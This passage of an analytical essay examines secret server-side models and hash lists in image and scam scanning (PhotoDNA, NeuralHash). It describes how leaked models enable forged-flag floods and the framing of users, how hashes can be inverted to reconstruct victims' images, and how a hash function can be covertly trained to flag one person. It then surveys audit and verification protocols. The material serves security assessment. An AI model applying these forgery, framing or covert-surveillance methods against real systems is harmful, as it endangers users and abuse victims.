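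Secrecy also kept outsiders from checking how well PhotoDNA worked. *Robustness and Collision-Resistance of PhotoDNA* notes that PhotoDNA's users carried out most of the evaluations and did not publish them. It cites a claimed false positive rate of less than one in a trillion and advises caution. The Commission gives a rate of no more than one in 50 billion "based on testing". Leblanc-Albarel and Preneel traced that figure to a 2019 report by Farid that doesn't explain how he obtained it. Microsoft, Farid and NCMEC had set the same limit as a requirement before PhotoDNA existed, so the figure may be a design goal later repeated as a measurement.

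NeuralHash became known much faster because it was already on people's devices. Apple also had a reason not to hide it, since it had promised that researchers could inspect the software. Eric Rescorla points out on Educated Guesswork that researchers could inspect it only if they could reverse-engineer NeuralHash.

NeuralHash is good evidence that anything shipped to users will become public, and PhotoDNA is good evidence that a secret shared with many companies eventually will too. Neither case closely resembles a model that runs only on one operator's servers. Such a model should stay secret longer, but the operator still has to protect it from intruders and its own staff.

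### What a stolen server model gives an attacker

An attacker who has both models can keep altering a harmless picture, checking both scores, until the local model flags it and the server model confirms the flag. If the server examines a reduced copy, as in Apple's design, the attacker can apply the same reduction before computing the server model's score. Fooling two models is harder than fooling one, so the changes may be more visible and more attempts may fail. But the attacker can discard failures without sending anything to the server, so they waste only computing time.

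In the earlier example of a flood of 100,000 forged items, reviewers had 21,031 items to examine when 20% of the forgeries passed the hidden server model. A flooder who has both models can send only forgeries that pass both, so all 100,000 reach the reviewers.

| Situation during the flood | Items for review | Reviewer hours |
|---|---|---|
| Server model secret, 20% transfer | 21,031 | 701 |
| Server model leaked | 101,031 | 3,370 |
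| No server check | 110,940 | 3,700 |

The eight reviewers in that example have 48 hours a day between them and use 34 on ordinary cases. With the remaining 14, they would need about eight months to clear the roughly 3,300 extra hours of review created by a one-day flood. The leaked model would still reject 9,909 mistaken flags from ordinary traffic, because its accuracy on items that nobody designed to fool it doesn't depend on secrecy.

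A framer gains even more from having the server model. Without it, requiring the server to confirm 16 of 31 matches cuts the risk to about 1 in 11,000 at a transfer rate of 20%. With both models, the framer can make sure that all 31 pictures pass before sending them. The framing still fails unless the victim saves the pictures and human reviewers mistake them for abuse.

A leak of the server model doesn't make evasion easier if the server examines only flagged items, because an evader needs to fool only the local model, which was already public. The leak matters if the server also checks random samples or pages with suspicious addresses, because an evader can then prepare a page that passes both models. Evidence from outside the item is still useful. A scammer with a copy of Chrome's server model could make a page look harmless, but couldn't give a new domain a long, clean history.

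An operator may not notice the theft, because the thief copies the model and leaves the original in place. One warning sign would be a rise in the share of confirmed flags that reviewers reject, which is normally about 10% in the running example. A flood of false flags would raise that share noticeably, but an attacker framing a single victim probably would not.

### Why a leaked list does different damage

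If the model stays secret but the list of hashes leaks, someone trying to frame a user no longer needs an abuse image to find a target hash. Someone who has abuse images and the local hash function can also check which images' hashes are missing from the list and keep only those images.

The people in the images may suffer more than the operator. Athalye used a neural network to recover rough faces and body shapes from PhotoDNA hashes. *Perceptual Hash Inversion Attacks on Image-Based Sexual Abuse Removal Tools* (2024) found that all commonly used perceptual hashes were vulnerable to its reconstruction attack, and concluded that services should protect the hashes almost as carefully as the images. Madden and colleagues found more resistance to such attacks. An operator should still plan for the possibility that images can be reconstructed from hashes, since one successful method is enough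 to expose victims.

The 2024 study proposes using private set intersection for services that let people report intimate images. A company would then learn only the reported hashes that match images it already stores and could not read the others.

Training a reconstruction network requires many images paired with their hashes, and anyone who can run the hash function can make such pairs. Because PhotoDNA's function has leaked, the secrecy of the hash lists is now the main protection against reconstruction. Longer hashes might reduce false matches, but Leblanc-Albarel and Preneel warn that they would also reveal more about each image.

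An operator can replace a leaked model but can't recall copies of a leaked list. Changing the hash function afterwards protects only images added later. A leaked list of scam addresses does much less harm, because most of the addresses soon become useless and none of them depicts a victim.

### What outsiders cannot check

Even if the server model never leaks, users can't see what it looks for, which is a separate objection from Kerckhoffs's. Keeping the model perfectly secret would protect best against forgers, but it would also give users the least assurance that the operator isn't searching for something else.

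Jain and colleagues show how hard such a search could be to find, even for someone with access to the model. They imagined a government agency that supplies the hash function for scanning phones. They trained the function to recognise copies of images, as usual, and also to give photos of one chosen person nearly the same hash. They repeated this for ten people, training on 100 photos of each.

The resulting models flagged about 67% of new photos of the chosen person. When the researchers converted the output into binary codes, as NeuralHash does, the models still flagged 66%, compared with under 1% for a model without the hidden purpose. With only 25 training photos, the rate fell to about 35%. A single model trained to find all ten people flagged 51% of their new photos.

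The agency can activate the search by adding just one image to the list. It can take a real illegal image and alter it slightly so that its hash matches the chosen person's. An auditor who looked at the image would see illegal material that belonged on the list.

The models with a hidden purpose performed as well as ordinary ones at their official task. In a test on 1.4 million images, a complete system with an ordinary model wrongly flagged about 2,873 images per million, and one with a hidden-purpose model wrongly flagged about 2,774. Adding the chosen person's images to the list raised the second figure by 0.3 per million. The hidden-purpose models did not react to faces in general, and their internal activity looked normal. The researchers acknowledge that an auditor who tested photos of the right person would easily discover the search, but the auditor would have to know whom to test.

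Apple's match threshold would offer little protection here. At a 67% recognition rate, a library with about 46 photos of the person would produce 31 matches, and many people have that many pictures of themselves. Apple's requirement for identical hashes would probably lower the recognition rate, since the study mostly allowed near matches.

An independent server hash could stop this attack, because a holiday photo looks nothing like the altered illegal image. But the agency might supply the server hash too, or demand that the operator switch it off. Outsiders can at least test photos on the local model, which they can't do with a hidden one.

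### What audits and published proofs can establish

Scheffler, Kulshrestha and Mayer (2023), in *Public Verification for Private Hash Matching*, divide the problem into trust in the list and trust in the software that uses it. They conclude that technology alone can't fully settle either, but describe protocols that let the public verify three things:

| What the protocol provides | Example | What remains uncertain |
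|---|---|---|
| Proof that outside groups approve the list | Child-safety organisations in several countries certify it | The groups could make mistakes or work together |
| Proof that a particular lawful item is not on the list | A newspaper asks about a photo of a protest | Someone has to know which item to ask about |
| Eventual notice to users of false matches | A user learns that a harmless photo matched | The notice comes after the match, and may help a forger |

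Scheffler and colleagues report that the protocols are practical and work with existing private matching systems. The protocols suit lists better than classifiers, because a classifier has no entries to certify, and proving that it ignores one protest photo gives little evidence of how it will treat the next.

Thomas and colleagues at Google take a different approach to lists, in which the organisation that supplies an entry signs it, so users can find out who was responsible. A Merkle tree lets users check that everyone has the same list. For a list with entries *a*, *b*, *c* and *d*, the operator hashes each entry, hashes the results in pairs and hashes those two results together to get one root, which it publishes. To prove that *b* is on the list, it supplies the hash of *a* and the combined hash of *c* and *d*. The user's device combines these with the hash of *b* and checks that it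 gets the published root. For 5 million entries, a proof needs only about 23 hashes.

A user who disagrees with a verdict can take the proof to a journalist or a judge, who can verify it without special access. Other auditors can examine the full list and the original items with the operator's permission. The design also uses cryptographic hashes, so forging a match is infeasible even for someone who knows the whole algorithm, but changing one pixel of a listed image avoids a match.

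This works because the device has access to the result. Apple's system would never have revealed a match to the phone, so the phone's owner would have had nothing to show a journalist.

Apple instead said that an independent auditor would review the system, MacRumors reported in 2021, and added that a participating child-safety organisation could carry out its own audit. These audits would have covered how Apple assembled the list, not what the images showed, and Apple proposed no equivalent check for the second hash. Rescorla doubted that verifying one component was worth much, because anyone who buys an Apple device must already trust Apple's hardware and the rest of its software.

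An operator could publish a cryptographic hash of the server model's weights and use attested hardware to prove that its servers run that version. This would expose undisclosed changes to the model, but it would not reveal whether the original version was trained to flag content for an undisclosed purpose.

Human review can stop a wrongful report if the reviewers are free to reject it. In the scenario that Jain and colleagues describe, the review comes too late because the agency itself receives the flagged photos. Reviewers at an independent organisation would be a better safeguard, though a government could also pressure them.

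### A checklist for assessing a hidden check

An assessor can start with the operator's security claims and ask which would still be true if attackers obtained the server model.

| Claim | After the server model leaks |
|---|---|
| The server removes accidental false flags | Still true |
| The server rejects forged flags | No longer true for forgeries built against both models |
| Random samples catch items that evade the local model | No longer true for items altered to pass both |
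| A site's history can expose a new scam page | Still true |
| The operator can't read matches below the threshold | Still true, because this depends on cryptographic keys |

The remaining questions concern how the operator would respond and who could hold it to account:

1. **How much protection depends on secrecy?** Have testers forge flags without the server's weights, then again with them. If success rises from 20% to nearly 100%, the operator should report both figures.
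2. **Who has a copy?** Count the machines, employees and outside companies with access to the weights. Do the same for the list, and store the two separately.
3. **How quickly can the operator replace the model?** Rehearse the whole process, including new error measurements and any hashes that other organisations must recompute. Check that forgeries made for the old model fail on the new one. A tested spare model that uses different features would save time.
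4. **What happens in the meantime?** Decide in advance which automatic actions to suspend. A browser can keep showing warnings, but a photo service should not disable accounts because of flags that the leaked model has confirmed.
5. **Who can audit the list, the model and the running software?** Record what each auditor can see and whether they can publish a critical finding. If nobody outside the company can examine the server check, users shouldn't count it as protection against the company or a government that controls it.
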